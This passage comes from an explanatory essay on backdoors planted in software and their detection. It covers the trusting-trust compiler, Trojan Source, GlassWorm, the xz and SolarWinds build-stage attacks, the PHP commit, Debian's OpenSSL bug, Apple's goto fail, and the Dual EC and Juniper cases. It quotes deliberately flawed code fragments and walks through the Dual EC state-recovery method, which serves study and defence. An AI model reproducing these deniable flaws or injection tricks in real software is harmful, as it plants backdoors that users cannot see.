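Karger and Schell did not build this compiler, which they estimated would cost perhaps five times as much as their other attacks. One of those, a working trap door, had taken about 18 hours of labour. They did test whether the manufacturer, Honeywell, would distribute a trap door without noticing. *Thirty Years Later* (Karger and Schell, 2002) describes how they put a disarmed trap door, one instruction away from being harmful, into the development system at MIT. Honeywell delivered it to the Pentagon. Their original report hinted at it, but nobody found it until about a year after publication, when it returned an odd error during a security audit at General Motors.

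The Pentagon's contract required Honeywell to supply the source code, so that the Pentagon could compile Multics itself. Recompiling would have removed an ordinary trap door in the compiled program, but not one that the compiler put back each time.

The known attacks on programming tools have mostly been simpler than Thompson's. In 2015 attackers persuaded developers to use a counterfeit copy of Xcode, Apple's tool for writing iPhone apps. The security company FireEye estimated that it added malicious code to more than 4,000 apps, and WeChat was among those infected. Neither this attack nor the build-stage attacks on SolarWinds and xz needed a compiler that reinfects itself. Wheeler does pass on a story about such a compiler from a programmer named Mike Stute, who tried for 15 days to remove a message from a program before he realised that a former graduate student had poisoned the compiler.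 Nobody seems to have confirmed the story.

Cox thinks attackers do not need Thompson's method because so many people run code from strangers without checking it. This is a plausible reason for the lack of known cases. Some cases may also remain undiscovered, since the method leaves so little to find.

### Checking one compiler with another

Thompson concluded that no amount of checking source code will protect people from code they did not create themselves. He was right that checking the source alone is not enough. Comparing the suspect binary with one built from the same source by a different compiler does not reveal tampering either, because two compilers translate the same source into different bytes even when neither has been tampered with.

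Henry Spencer, a Canadian programmer, suggested a way around this in a very short posting in 1998. Wheeler (2010), in *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, developed it into a full procedure with a formal proof. In the common case, where a compiler is supposed to have compiled itself, it works like this:

1. A second compiler, which the checker has reason to trust, translates the suspect compiler's source code. The result differs from the suspect compiler byte for byte, but it should do the same job, since both are supposed to come from the same source.
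2. This new compiler translates the same source code again.
3. The checker compares the final result with the suspect compiler, bit by bit.

If the suspect compiler has no backdoor, the two files are identical, because the compiler from step 1 follows the same instructions and so produces the same output from the same input. If the suspect compiler contains Thompson's tricks, its file has extra code that is missing from the file from step 2, which was made without the suspect compiler. With the compilers in Cox's simulator, the check should produce a file of 10,724 bytes, compared with 12,918 bytes for the backdoored one.

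If the suspect compiler was built by a different compiler, or by an older version of itself, the checker uses that parent compiler's source code in step 1 and the suspect compiler's source code in step 2.

A match proves that the suspect compiler corresponds to its source code. It does not prove that the source code is harmless, so someone still has to read it, but programmers do that routinely, whereas reading a large compiled program is extremely laborious. The proof depends on several assumptions:

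- The second compiler, the computer it runs on and the program that compares the files must contain nothing that interferes with this particular check. The checker must also have obtained the right source code and the right copy of the suspect compiler.
- The second compiler must give the source code the meaning its authors intended, including any non-standard features of the language that they used.
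- The compiler that the source describes must always produce the same output from the same input. One that adds the current time to every file, for example, would fail the comparison even if it were honest.

Wheeler therefore recommends first trying to rebuild the suspect compiler exactly as its makers say they built it. In his experience this often fails, because organisations have not recorded everything that went into the build. If the rebuild fails, a mismatch in the main check is only weak evidence of an attack. A successful rebuild does not show that the compiler is clean, because Thompson's compromised compiler would also pass this test.

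Wheeler argues that the procedure does more than move trust from one compiler to another, because an attacker would have to corrupt both in a coordinated way, and the defender can choose the second compiler after the attack has happened. That compiler may be slow, or even malicious in some other respect, as long as it does not interfere with this check. Some risk remains because, as Cox points out, matching files mean either that both compilers are clean or that both have the same backdoor.

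Wheeler tried the procedure on four compilers, including a small one he had corrupted on purpose and GCC, the large compiler that builds most of Linux. The first public use by other people that he knows of involved GNU Mes, a small C compiler intended as a starting point for rebuilding a whole operating system from source. Its developers used three versions of GCC on three Linux distributions and got identical files each time. Wheeler welcomed this but thought it added only limited confidence, because the systems had so much in common.

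Go's developers avoid the problem differently, by always building the Go compiler with an earlier release, in a chain that goes back to a version written in C. Anyone can repeat the chain, and Cox notes that the compiler never has to compile itself, so a backdoor that exists only in the compiled program cannot persist. The chain still begins with a C compiler, which someone has to check.

Neither approach extends easily to hardware. Thompson warned that a backdoor in a processor's internal instructions would be almost impossible to detect. Wheeler says his method could apply to chips in principle, but showing that two chips are identical is much harder than showing that two files are.

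### Code that looks different on the screen

A flaw can also be in the source code while the screen shows the reader something else. In November 2021 two Cambridge researchers, Nicholas Boucher and Ross Anderson, described attacks that do this by changing how the code appears. According to *Trojan Source*, their announcement in Light Blue Touchpaper, someone who wanted to smuggle in a vulnerability before then could try an unobtrusive bug in an obscure piece of code, as the contest entrants did.

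Their attacks use Unicode, the standard that gives a number to every character in the world's writing systems. Hebrew and Arabic run from right to left, so Unicode includes invisible control characters that change the direction of the text. A compiler reads characters in the order in which the file stores them, while an editor displays them in the order that the control characters dictate. Boucher and Anderson illustrate the difference with the first letters of the alphabet:

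| What the file stores | What the screen shows |
|---|---|
| a b c | a b c |
| (start right-to-left) a b c (end) | c b a |
| (start right-to-left) (start left-to-right) a b c (end) (start left-to-right) d e f (end) (end) | d e f a b c |

The last row matters most because the groups change places while each stays readable, which lets an attacker move whole words and symbols along a line.

Compilers normally reject stray control characters, but they accept them in comments, which are notes for human readers, and in strings, which are pieces of text that the program uses. A line can therefore appear to contain a security check that is actually part of a comment, which the compiler ignores, and a reviewer may approve the code believing that the check will run.

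Look-alike letters can hide a flaw in a similar way without moving any text. The Latin letter "a" and the Cyrillic letter "а" look the same in most fonts, but their Unicode numbers are 97 and 1072. A programmer could define two functions that both appear to be called `pay`, one spelled with the Cyrillic letter, and the compiler would treat them as unrelated. A reader who had checked one would have no reason to suspect that a later line used the other.

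Boucher and Anderson built working examples in C, C++, C# and other languages. TechTarget's *Trojan Source bugs enable 'invisible' source code poisoning* reported that the problem affected nearly every popular language. The researchers warned 19 organisations before publishing, and Vumetric's *‘Trojan Source’ Hides Invisible Bugs in Source Code* (2021) reported that many of them were releasing updates to compilers, editors and code repositories. Rust's compiler now rejects direction-changing characters in comments and strings by default, and GitHub shows a warning on files that contain them.

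A complete ban on changes of text direction would be awkward for programmers who write comments in Hebrew or Arabic. Boucher and Anderson (2023), in *Some Vulnerabilities are Invisible*, recommend that languages forbid a change of direction only if it is still in effect when the comment or string ends. They also want editors and code-hosting sites to mark direction changes and suspicious mixtures of alphabets. *What You See Is Not Always What You Get* (2024) points to the Unicode Consortium's published lists of easily confused characters, which can be used to spot look-alikes.

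### Invisible characters in real attacks

Attackers have since used invisible characters on a large scale, though more crudely. The GlassWorm campaign spreads malware that steals programmers' passwords and cryptocurrency. The security company Koi Security first reported it in October 2025, but The Hacker News' *GlassWorm Supply-Chain Attack Abuses 72 Open VSX Extensions to Target Developers* (2026) traces the same technique to packages from March 2025. Another company, Aikido Security, found at least 151 GitHub repositories that the attackers had altered between 3 and 9 March 2026. Aikido suspects the real number was much higher, because many affected repositories had disappeared before it published its findings.

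The attackers use variation selectors, characters that normally set which version of the preceding symbol appears, such as the plain or coloured form of an emoji. Most editors don't display them. The ranges given in Tom's Hardware's *Invisible malicious code attacks 151 GitHub repos and VS Code* contain 256 characters, one for each possible byte value, so a string that looks empty can hold an entire program. A short piece of visible code decodes the string and runs it.

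This visible part makes GlassWorm easier to catch than Trojan Source, because a careful reader can notice that the program decodes a seemingly empty string and executes the result. The attackers seem to have relied on nobody looking that closely. They surrounded the insertions with small, ordinary changes in each project's style. Aikido suspects they wrote these changes with AI language models, since producing 151 by hand would have been impractical.

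GlassWorm's hidden programs are malware and are not disguised as honest mistakes. Reports on the campaign describe hidden text but not reordered code, so they do not confirm any real use of Boucher and Anderson's main attack. The group has also published some editor extensions that were harmless at first and began installing a malicious companion in a later update. The group was still active in October 2026, when *Pretty Themes, Hidden Loaders* (Boychenko, 2026) reported two malicious editor themes with thousands of installations between them, along with related extensions.

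### Different hiding places, different checks

Inspecting the source code cannot reveal Thompson's backdoor, because the source does not contain it. Defenders have to check whether the compiled program matches the source. They can do this with Wheeler's procedure or, for software in general, with reproducible builds, which let other people rebuild a program and confirm that they get the same file.

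That comparison cannot detect Trojan Source, because the program matches the source and only the human reader sees something different. But the deceptive characters are all in the file, so a simple automatic search can find them if it covers the right ones. A tool that looked only for direction changes and mixed alphabets, the checks Boucher and Anderson recommended, would miss GlassWorm's variation selectors.

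Some hiding places are also easier for the attacker to explain away than others. A programmer who types in two alphabets might plausibly have entered a Cyrillic letter by accident, but thousands of invisible characters that decode into a working program have no innocent explanation. The flaw in Åkesson's warhead program from the 2015 contest could still be explained as a mistake, and the program would also pass both checks, since it contains only ordinary characters and the compiled version does exactly what the source code specifies.

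## Has anyone planted a subtle flaw in real software?

In March 2024 a programmer looking into slow logins found a backdoor in xz, a compression tool that comes with most Linux systems. A volunteer who had spent more than two years winning the project's trust had planted it. The attack, catalogued as CVE-2024-3094, is one of the best-documented cases of a planted backdoor in widely used software. Most of it differed from the contest programs because the attacker hid the harmful code inside data instead of making it look innocent, but one small part, a single full stop, did resemble them.

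### How a stranger became a maintainer

Lasse Collin designed the xz file format with others between 2005 and 2008, then maintained the software more or less alone as an unpaid hobby. Nearly 30,000 Debian and Ubuntu packages used xz, according to *Human-Certified Module Repositories for the AI Age* (2026). Russ Cox reconstructed the takeover of the project in *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024).

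Somebody using the name Jia Tan sent a first patch to the xz mailing list on 29 October 2021, adding a settings file for text editors. More patches followed, and even in retrospect they seem fine. In April 2022, three days after Jia Tan sent another patch, a stranger called Jigar Kumar complained that it was taking too long. Collin had accepted four of Jia Tan's patches by then.

In May another stranger, Dennis Ens, asked whether anyone still maintained the Java version of xz. Collin apologised for his slowness and said that Jia Tan might get a bigger role. Kumar wrote that nothing would progress until there was a new maintainer. Collin answered that he had long-term mental health problems and that xz was an unpaid hobby project. Ens said he was sorry to hear it, then suggested that Collin hand over one of the two versions. By the end of June Collin was describing Jia Tan as "practically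 a co-maintainer already".

Cox thinks Kumar and Ens were probably fakes, created to push Collin into giving up control. He cites the journalist Brian Krebs, who observed that many of the email addresses involved never appeared anywhere else on the internet, even in leaked data.

Jia Tan was adding changes directly to the repository by December 2022. Przymus and Durieux (2025), in *Wolves in the Repository*, sorted the persona's contributions line by line and found mostly documentation and translations, which attract little scrutiny. They counted only eight malicious commits. Jia Tan also answered users' questions, announced releases and moved the project to GitHub, which gave the persona ownership of the project's account there. Some of these chores gave Jia Tan other useful powers. In March 2023, for example, Jia Tan arranged to receive the bug reports from OSS-Fuzz, Google's free service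 for testing open-source programs with random input.

Przymus and Durieux concede that an enthusiastic honest volunteer would have looked much the same. Collin had too little time, and someone competent was offering to help, so it is hard to see what he should have noticed in 2022.

### A payload in two places

The attacker divided the backdoor between the repository and the release archive, the packaged source code that distributors download for each new version.

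Two test files added to the xz repository in February 2024 contained the compiled backdoor and the scripts to install it, all compressed and scrambled. A compression program is tested on damaged and unusual files, and xz already had a directory full of them. The directory's description, written long before Jia Tan arrived, explained that many of the files had been made by hand and had no better "source code" than themselves. Nobody could be expected to read such files. Freund (2024) reported in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* that no test in version 5.6.0 used the two new ones.

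The release archive contained the piece that unpacked them, an altered copy of a standard build file called `build-to-host.m4`. As LWN explains, projects that use the common build system Autoconf publish archives with generated files that the repository lacks, so an extra file was nothing unusual. The attacker had raised the file's version number from 3 to 30, updated the copyright year and added some lines that were about as hard to read as the rest. Cox took them apart in *The xz attack shell script* (2024):

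1. The altered build file searches the source code for a file containing a certain pattern of characters. Only one matches, a test file that is supposed to be corrupt.
2. It swaps a few byte values, which repairs the corruption, then decompresses the result and runs it as a script.
3. This script cuts pieces out of the other test file, joins them, unscrambles them and gets a second, longer script.
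4. The second script checks that it is running on the right kind of machine and is building a package for a Debian-type or Red Hat-type system. If so, it rewrites the build instructions to add the compiled backdoor to liblzma, the part of xz that other programs load. Otherwise it stops.

An investigator who compiled xz by hand would therefore have got a clean copy. If they had read the repository, they would have found two opaque test files and nothing that ran them.

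### What the backdoor allowed

The target was OpenSSH, the program administrators use to log in to remote machines. Debian, Fedora and several other distributions modify OpenSSH to report to systemd, the program that starts and stops services, and systemd's library loaded the compression library liblzma. The attacker reached this heavily guarded program through a library that OpenSSH itself does not use.

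A library normally can't change how the program that loads it works. The attacker got around this with indirect functions, a feature that lets a library pick the fastest version of a function when a program starts. The selection code runs early enough that the program's table of function addresses can still be changed. At that point, the backdoor replaced the address of `RSA_public_decrypt`, which OpenSSH uses to check signatures, with the address of its own code.

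Someone called Hans Jansen had contributed the indirect functions in June 2023. Przymus and Durieux leave open whether this was a genuine improvement. Cox is more suspicious because Jansen has no other presence on the internet and came back in March 2024 to urge Debian to adopt the new version.

The cryptographer Filippo Valsorda published a preliminary analysis of the backdoor, which Patrakov (2024) forwarded to the mailing list where Freund had reported it. The attacker hides a command in a certificate and presents it to the server at the start of a login. The backdoor checks that the command is signed with the attacker's private key and then runs it, before anyone has logged in. If the signature is wrong, OpenSSH carries on as usual, so nobody else could use the backdoor or find infected servers by probing them over the network. Valsorda called it a nightmare scenario: "malicious, competent,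 authorized upstream in a widely used library".

### Half a second

Andres Freund, who works on the PostgreSQL database at Microsoft, was running a test version of Debian when he noticed that SSH logins were using a lot of processor time. A failed login that had taken 0.299 seconds now took 0.807. He had also seen errors from Valgrind, a tool that finds memory mistakes in programs. He traced both problems to liblzma. He first thought someone had tampered with Debian's package, but then found the same code in the archives that xz itself published. He told Debian privately on 28 March 2024 and posted a public warning the next day.

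The delay came from the backdoor's slow search through the program's tables for the function it wanted to replace. The attacker had already dealt with the Valgrind errors, which began to appear on Red Hat's systems on 4 March. On 8 March Jia Tan committed a fake fix as a distraction. The real fix came the next day, in new versions of the two test files. Jia Tan said that the old files contained random data from a personal machine, and that a fixed seed would make the new ones easier to reproduce.

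On 29 February, a developer proposed that systemd's library stop loading liblzma automatically, and the project accepted the change on 5 March. The change would have defeated the attack on any distribution that adopted it. The security researcher Kevin Beaumont has speculated that the attacker hurried because of this proposal, which might account for the bugs.

The backdoored versions reached mainly test editions, including Debian's and a beta of Fedora 40. Red Hat reinstalled all of its own machines that ran an affected Fedora version and found no evidence of further tampering. Przymus and Durieux know of no case in which anyone used the backdoor. Collin reviewed the commits and published clean releases on 29 May, according to *xz backdoor*, his account on the Tukaani project's website.

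### The stray full stop

Jia Tan made a much smaller change in late February. Linux has a feature called Landlock, which lets a program give up access that it does not need, so that an attacker who takes over the program can do less damage. The xz command can use it. To find out whether a machine supports Landlock, one of xz's build configurations tries to compile a tiny C program that mentions the feature. If the program compiles, the configuration switches the protection on. Jia Tan's version of the tiny program contained these lines:

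```
#include <sys/prctl.h>
.
void my_sandbox(void)
```

The full stop is not valid C, so the test program never compiles, even on machines that support Landlock. The configuration therefore builds xz without Landlock. No error appears, because a failed compilation normally means that the system lacks Landlock support. A comment above the lines gives a sensible reason for the test: some systems have the Landlock header file but lack the functions it declares.

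This change could almost be a contest entry, because the code is short and readable, the purpose is plausible, and the error looks like a typo. At least one reader missed the error while looking for it. In a comment on *Free software's not-so-eXZellent adventure*, AlecTavi (2024) describes reading the change on a phone after learning that it disabled Landlock, then copying out the C code to test it. AlecTavi accidentally removed the full stop along with the plus signs that mark added lines, so the code compiled. Collin may have missed the error too. The repository lists him as the committer, and in his later review he found no signs that anyone had forged that field, according to Tukaani.

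The flaw did little damage. sjw (2024), who relayed the discovery from GitHub commenters, noted that it was only in version 5.6.1 and only in the CMake build configuration, which no distribution was known to use. Cox could not tell what the flaw was for, since Landlock protects the xz command and has nothing to do with the attack on OpenSSH. Perhaps the attacker was preparing something else.

The payload would stay hidden as long as nobody unpacked the test files, but once found it could not be passed off as a mistake. The full stop was in plain view in the repository and would have been easy to explain as an accident. A participant in *Sourceware mitigating and preventing the next xz-backdoor*, a discussion among developers of programming tools, noticed that the attacker had dared to change far less in the CMake file than in the build file from the release archive. In Thomas and Francillon's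 scheme, the other seven or so malicious commits are the grounds for suspecting that the full stop was deliberate. Collin's correction removes that one character, and its message reads "Fix sabotaged Landlock sandbox check." If Jia Tan had done nothing else, the correction would probably have been recorded as fixing a typing error.

### SolarWinds and PHP

SolarWinds, a Texas company, makes Orion, which organisations use to monitor their networks. Attackers broke into the company in 2019, without having to persuade a maintainer of anything, and later put a program on the server that built Orion. CrowdStrike, a security company that analysed this program in January 2021, found that it waited for a build to start, swapped one source file for a version with a backdoor, and put the original back afterwards. The attackers had also suppressed compiler warnings about their code, in case a developer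 noticed them.

SolarWinds signed the result as genuine and began distributing it in March 2020, and up to 18,000 customers installed it. The backdoor stayed idle for up to two weeks on each new machine, then disguised its messages as Orion's own traffic. FireEye discovered it in December 2020 while investigating a breach of its own network, and the US government later blamed Russia's foreign intelligence service. Reading SolarWinds' stored source code would not have revealed the backdoor because, as with Thompson's compiler, it was added during the build.

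The attack on PHP, the language behind a large share of the world's websites, was cruder. On 28 March 2021 a commit appeared in its official repository under the name of Rasmus Lerdorf, PHP's creator. It was labeled a typo fix, but the new lines ran any code that a visitor sent in a request header called "User-Agentt", with a doubled t, if the text began with "zerodium", the name of a company that bought undisclosed vulnerabilities. Developers who routinely read new commits noticed within hours and removed the lines. The attacker put them back under the name of another leading developer, Nikita Popov, and the developers removed them again before any release.

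Popov first assumed that someone had broken into the server, but about a week later he thought a leak of the project's user database was more likely. The attacker used forged names, as in the 2003 attempt on Linux, but put much less effort into the code.

| Case | Entry point | Disguise | Time undetected | Means of discovery |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| xz backdoor | Repository and release archive, through a trusted maintainer | Compiled code inside test files, unpacked by an altered build file | About five weeks | Slow logins and memory errors |
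| xz full stop | Repository, through the same maintainer | One wrong character in a compatibility test | About a month | People searched the maintainer's other commits after the backdoor became public |
| SolarWinds | Build server | Source file swapped only during the build; signed update | More than eight months after release | A customer investigated its own break-in |
| PHP | Repository, under developers' names | A message about a typo | Hours | Developers read new commits |

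The five weeks for xz are based on Cox, who dates the malicious test files to 23 February. Przymus and Durieux date the first backdoor commit a month earlier. The order of the table is also a poor measure of skill. The xz attackers were arguably more careful than the SolarWinds attackers, but their backdoor was found much sooner because it slowed down something a programmer happened to be measuring.

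### Who was behind xz?

Nobody has publicly identified Jia Tan, which is presumably a pseudonym. *Half a Second* (Mastronardi, 2026, last updated in July), a book about the case, says whoever used the name may never be identified.

Many people suspect a government was responsible. The security company Akamai, in *XZ Utils 后门* ("The XZ Utils backdoor"), reasons that usually only state-backed attackers run such long operations, but it names no country. The attacker's patience and the locked access would fit either an intelligence service or a well-funded criminal group that planned to sell access, so they are only weak evidence that a government was involved.

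Analysts also looked at the time zones recorded with Jia Tan's commits. Most are eight hours ahead of Greenwich, which would fit China, but a few are two or three hours ahead, which would fit eastern Europe. Anyone can set a computer's clock to a false zone, and Collin points to mundane reasons the zones might vary, such as one person committing work in another's name with permission. It also isn't certain how many people were involved. BTW Media cautions that the public record does not prove that all the personas belonged to one person or organisation, and Przymus and Durieux found no direct links between the accounts.

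Similar takeovers have happened on a smaller scale. In 2018 the owner of event-stream, a popular JavaScript component, gave control to a volunteer who had offered to maintain it. The volunteer added a dependency that later stole cryptocurrency, and nobody noticed for about two months. Cox therefore seems to go too far in describing xz as apparently the first serious known supply-chain attack on widely used open-source software. In April 2024 the OpenJS Foundation, which supports JavaScript projects, reported that strangers with little prior involvement in one of its projects had been emailing to ask to become maintainers. It refused them, and nobody has shown that they were connected with Jia Tan.

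As of October 2026, no one appears to have publicly confirmed another operation as long and elaborate as the one against xz. Other supply-chain attacks continued that month. *Claude Code extension poisoned with persistent SSH backdoor* (Markovic, 2026) reported a tampered extension for a popular coding agent, and *AOMEI Backupper Compromised in Short-Burst Supply Chain Campaign* (Arghire, 2026) described repeated tampering with a backup program. Both attacks delivered malware, but neither is known to have begun with a patient takeover like Jia Tan's.

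### The cases nobody has found

We know about all of these cases because something went wrong for the attacker, so they are a biased sample. If people discover a share *p* of all planted flaws, *n* known cases imply about *n*/*p* in total. Ten known cases would mean about 20 if half are discovered, and about 1,000 if one in a hundred is. Nobody knows *p*, so the number of known cases is only a minimum for the total.

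Some kinds of planted flaw are also probably more likely to be found than others. A conspicuous backdoor like PHP's is easy to find, but a wrong character in a rarely used check may go unnoticed for years and then count as an ordinary bug. The known cases therefore overrepresent attacks that were crude, unlucky or too elaborate to pass off as mistakes. Some suspected cases, such as the random number generator Dual_EC_DRBG and its use in Juniper's firewalls, are hard to count because people still disagree about what was intended. Others are public only because the people who planted the flaws announced them, as researchers at the University of Minnesota did after sending flawed patches to Linux developers.

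The times in the table have the same bias. A flaw planted ten years ago that nobody has noticed cannot appear there, so the average time undetected is probably shorter for known cases than for all planted flaws.

Akamai asks what it would mean if something like the xz attack had happened before. The question is fair because Freund's discovery took a good deal of luck, which suggests that other backdoors may have gone unnoticed, though a single case can't show how many. After the attack, programmers wrote a tool called distro-backdoor-scanner to audit the packages in Linux distributions. It may find build files altered in the way Jia Tan altered one, but it is much less likely to find a flaw as small as an added full stop.

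## How can anyone tell sabotage from an honest mistake?

Two well-known security flaws would have done well in the Underhanded C Contest, although most people regard them as accidents. From 2006 to 2008, one caused Debian's software to produce encryption keys that were easy to guess. The other, a single repeated line of code, stopped Apple's devices from properly checking the identity of secure websites.

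### Debian's predictable keys

OpenSSL is a library of encryption routines that many programs share. It makes secret keys from random numbers, which it produces by mixing unpredictable data into a pool. In April 2006 a Debian user ran OpenSSL under Valgrind, the memory-checking tool from the xz case, and Valgrind warned that OpenSSL was reading memory before anything had been stored there.

Kurt Roeckx, who maintained Debian's copy of OpenSSL, traced the warnings to two places in the code. As LWN showed, both contained the same instruction:

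```
MD_Update(&m,buf,j);
```

The instruction mixes the contents of `buf` into the pool. In one place, `buf` held leftover memory, which added little, and OpenSSL's developers had already provided a switch to turn that line off for tools like Valgrind. In the other, it held the random data that OpenSSL had gathered. According to a comment on the blog Financial Cryptography (2008), the user had asked only about the harmless line, and Roeckx extended the change to the vital one.

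Removing the vital line disabled the function for adding randomness. Only the process ID, the number Linux gives to each running program, still varied. It had at most 32,768 possible values (*Random Number Bug in Debian Linux*, 2008), so an attacker could generate every possible key of a given type in advance and try them all.

The change history suggests an honest mistake. On 1 May 2006 Roeckx posted both lines to a public OpenSSL mailing list, proposed removing them and admitted he had "no idea what effect this really has". *Debian, OpenSSL, and a lack of cooperation* (Edge, 2008) reports that the few replies raised no objection. One, from an OpenSSL address, favoured removing the lines if that helped with debugging. Debian's *Bug#363516* (2006) records that Roeckx closed the user's report on 14 May.

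Ben Laurie, a member of OpenSSL's core team, later objected that Roeckx had used the wrong list and should have submitted a patch to the project. But OpenSSL's website described the list as the place to discuss development. In *Lessons from the Debian/OpenSSL Fiasco*, Russ Cox explains why the error was easy to make. The two calls looked almost identical, and OpenSSL's developers had marked one as dispensable, so it was reasonable to think the other was too.

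A saboteur could have asked the same question to create an excuse, but would have risked someone on the list explaining what the second line did. Roeckx also acted under his own name and stayed on as maintainer for years after Luciano Bello discovered the flaw. Debian's advisory, *New openssl packages fix predictable random number generator* (Weimer, 2008), attributed the flaw to an incorrect change specific to Debian.

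### Apple's extra line

In February 2014 Apple released an urgent update without explaining what was wrong. Programmers soon found the answer in source code that Apple itself had published:

```
if ((err = SSLHashSHA1.update(&hashCtx, &signedParams)) != 0)
        goto fail;
        goto fail;
```

In C, an `if` without braces controls only the next statement. The first `goto fail` therefore runs only after an error, but the second, despite its indentation, runs even when there is no error. It jumps past the step that checks the server's signature. Since the previous step succeeded, `err` still holds the value for success, and the function accepts the connection.

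The signature is supposed to prove that the temporary key for a connection comes from the owner of the website's certificate. Without this check, somebody who controlled the network between a user and a bank could present the bank's real certificate with their own key, then read the traffic. Adam Langley, a Google engineer, explained the flaw in *Apple's SSL/TLS bug* (ImperialViolet, 2014) and built a test site that signed with the wrong key. Any browser that loaded the site was vulnerable.

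The flaw met most of the contest's criteria. It was short, sat in the middle of error-checking code and had no effect on connections to legitimate websites. Langley found that neither of two common compilers warned about the skipped code, even with the option meant to enable all warnings. The flaw was also hard to test for, because the test required a server built to misbehave at one particular stage of the connection.

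Langley believed it was a mistake and felt sorry for whoever had slipped in an editor. A duplicated line is a common result of careless copying or of merging two versions of a file. But there is much less public evidence about intent than in the Debian case. Comparing Apple's releases shows that the line first appeared in version 10.9 of its desktop system and in some version of iOS 6, but not who added it or what else that person changed. The computer scientist Steven Bellovin asked in *Goto Fail* (2014) whether the line was malicious or accidental, but no one can tell from the code alone. Thomas and Francillon made the same point about deniable backdoors in general.

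### A random number generator with a possible master key

The US standards agency NIST published the Dual_EC_DRBG generator, usually called Dual EC, in 2006 as one of four approved ways to generate random numbers. It worked as specified, so the doubts about it concern the specification.

Dual EC uses an elliptic curve, which is a set of points (x, y) that satisfy a certain equation, with a rule for adding two points to get a third. Multiplying a point P by a whole number s means adding s copies of P together, and the result is written sP. A computer can do this quickly even when s is enormous, but nobody knows a practical way to find s from P and sP on a curve of the size used here. Much modern encryption depends on this difficulty.

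The standard fixes two points, P and Q. The generator keeps a secret number s, its state, and repeats two steps, where x(…) means the first coordinate of a point:

```
output     = x(sQ), without its first 16 bits
next state = x(sP)
```

Suppose somebody knows a number e for which P = eQ. Then sP = s(eQ) = e(sQ), so multiplying the point behind the output by e gives the point behind the next state. The attack works as follows:

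1. The attacker sees an output and tries all 65,536 possibilities for the missing 16 bits.
2. For each candidate x, the curve's equation gives at most two matching points, which differ only in the sign of y. Either will do, because both lead to the same next state.
3. The attacker multiplies the point by e and takes the first coordinate. For the right candidate, this is the generator's next state.
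4. A little more output shows which candidate is right, and the attacker can then compute everything the generator will produce.

The same calculation works on a tiny curve, y² = x³ + 2x + 2, where only remainders after division by 17 count. Let Q be (5, 1) and e be 7, so that P = 7Q = (0, 6). If the state is 3, the output is x(3Q) = 10 (with no bits removed), and the next state is x(3P) = 6. An attacker who sees the 10 finds the point (10, 6) from the equation and multiplies it by 7 to get (6, 3). The new state is 6, so the next output is x(6Q) = 16. Anybody could find e here by trying every number up to 18, but the real curve has roughly 2²⁵⁶ points.

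Shumow and Ferguson, two Microsoft researchers, presented this attack in *On the Possibility of a Back Door* at a cryptography conference in 2007. They noted that a suitable e must exist for any Q on this curve, and that the standard did not say where its Q came from. Whoever chose the points could have started with a secret e and calculated one point from the other. The designers could have ruled this out by deriving Q from public data through a scrambling function, so that nobody would know e. The standard described such a procedure for users who wanted their own points.

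Project Bullrun's *Dual EC DRBG*, a website that collects evidence about the generator, reports that patent filings show the Canadian company Certicom already knew of the backdoor by 2005. The filings also show that the US National Security Agency (NSA), which designed Dual EC, had been told about it by then, but NIST still approved the generator.

In September 2013 the New York Times reported on documents leaked by Edward Snowden, a former NSA contractor. The article described a 2006 standard with a fatal weakness that two Microsoft cryptographers had found in 2007, but it did not name Dual EC. According to *Dual EC DRBG*, an archived Wikipedia article, the leaked memos indicated that the NSA had worked to become the standard's sole editor. NIST replied that it would not deliberately weaken a standard. It advised against using Dual EC that month and revoked its support in 2014, saying that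 it no longer fully trusted the assumptions behind the generator's security.

Most of the evidence points to the NSA having planted the weakness. The agency chose the points, gave no public derivation for Q and pressed for the standard's adoption. Bernstein, Lange and Niederhagen (2015) titled their paper on it *Dual EC: A Standardized Back Door*. Reuters reported in 2013 that the NSA had paid the company RSA Security $10 million in a deal that made Dual EC the default in one of RSA's products. But nobody has publicly produced the e that goes with the standard's Q, so the conclusion depends on the leaked memos and the agency's conduct.

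### Juniper changes the lock, then somebody else does

Juniper Networks used Dual EC in ScreenOS, the operating system of its NetScreen devices. Companies and governments used the devices for virtual private networks (VPNs), which encrypt traffic between offices. In December 2015 Juniper announced that it had found unauthorised code in ScreenOS that could let an attacker decrypt this traffic.

In *Where Did I Leave My Keys?*, Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues (2018) compared dozens of versions of the software and found that somebody had made a tiny change to the encryption in 2012, replacing Q. The intruder also changed the expected answer in a built-in test, which would otherwise have failed. The generator's output looked as random as before, so no amount of testing it would have revealed the new Q.

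Replacing Q would have achieved little if ScreenOS had worked as Juniper said it did. In 2013 Juniper had reassured customers that it used Dual EC only to supply starting values to a second generator, called X9.31. An attacker would then never see Dual EC's output. But the program never ran the second generator. Simplified from the reconstruction by Checkoway and colleagues, the code looked like this:

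```
index = 0;
prng_reseed();               /* also sets index to 32 */
for (; index <= 31; index += 8)
        /* store 8 bytes from X9.31 in output */
```

The loop is supposed to fill 32 bytes of memory with numbers from X9.31. The function `prng_reseed` temporarily puts 32 bytes from Dual EC in the same memory, then copies them to where X9.31 needs them. But it also uses the loop's variable, `index`, and leaves it at 32, so the loop ends without writing anything and the rest of ScreenOS receives Dual EC's raw output.

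Several experienced researchers suspected a bug in this routine but did not find it until Willem Pinckaers noticed the shared variable. The laboratory that certified ScreenOS under US federal standards had missed it too.

The attacker also needs to see enough of the generator's output. When a VPN connection begins, each side sends a nonce, a random number that anyone watching can read. ScreenOS used to send 20-byte nonces, but recovering the generator's state is impractical with fewer than about 26 bytes. The version that introduced Dual EC, released in October 2008, lengthened the nonces to 32 bytes. Most devices on the internet used 20, and Checkoway and colleagues knew of no security advantage in longer nonces. They put their own Q into a real NetScreen device and decrypted three kinds of VPN connection, each from its own recorded traffic.

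| Change to ScreenOS | Benefit to someone who knows e | Possible innocent reason |
|---|---|---|
| 2008: Dual EC, with a Q chosen by Juniper | Makes the next state predictable | NIST had approved the generator |
| 2008: fresh starting values on every call, instead of every 10,000 calls | Makes Dual EC run every time | Changing them more often sounds safer |
| 2008: shared loop variable and memory | Exposes the raw output | Ordinary programming error |
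| 2008: nonces of 32 bytes instead of 20 | Reveals enough of the output | The new generator produced 32 bytes at a time |
| 2008: a queue of nonces made in advance | Often allows decryption from one connection alone | Faster connections |
| 2012: a new Q and a new test answer | Gives access to whoever chose the new Q | None |

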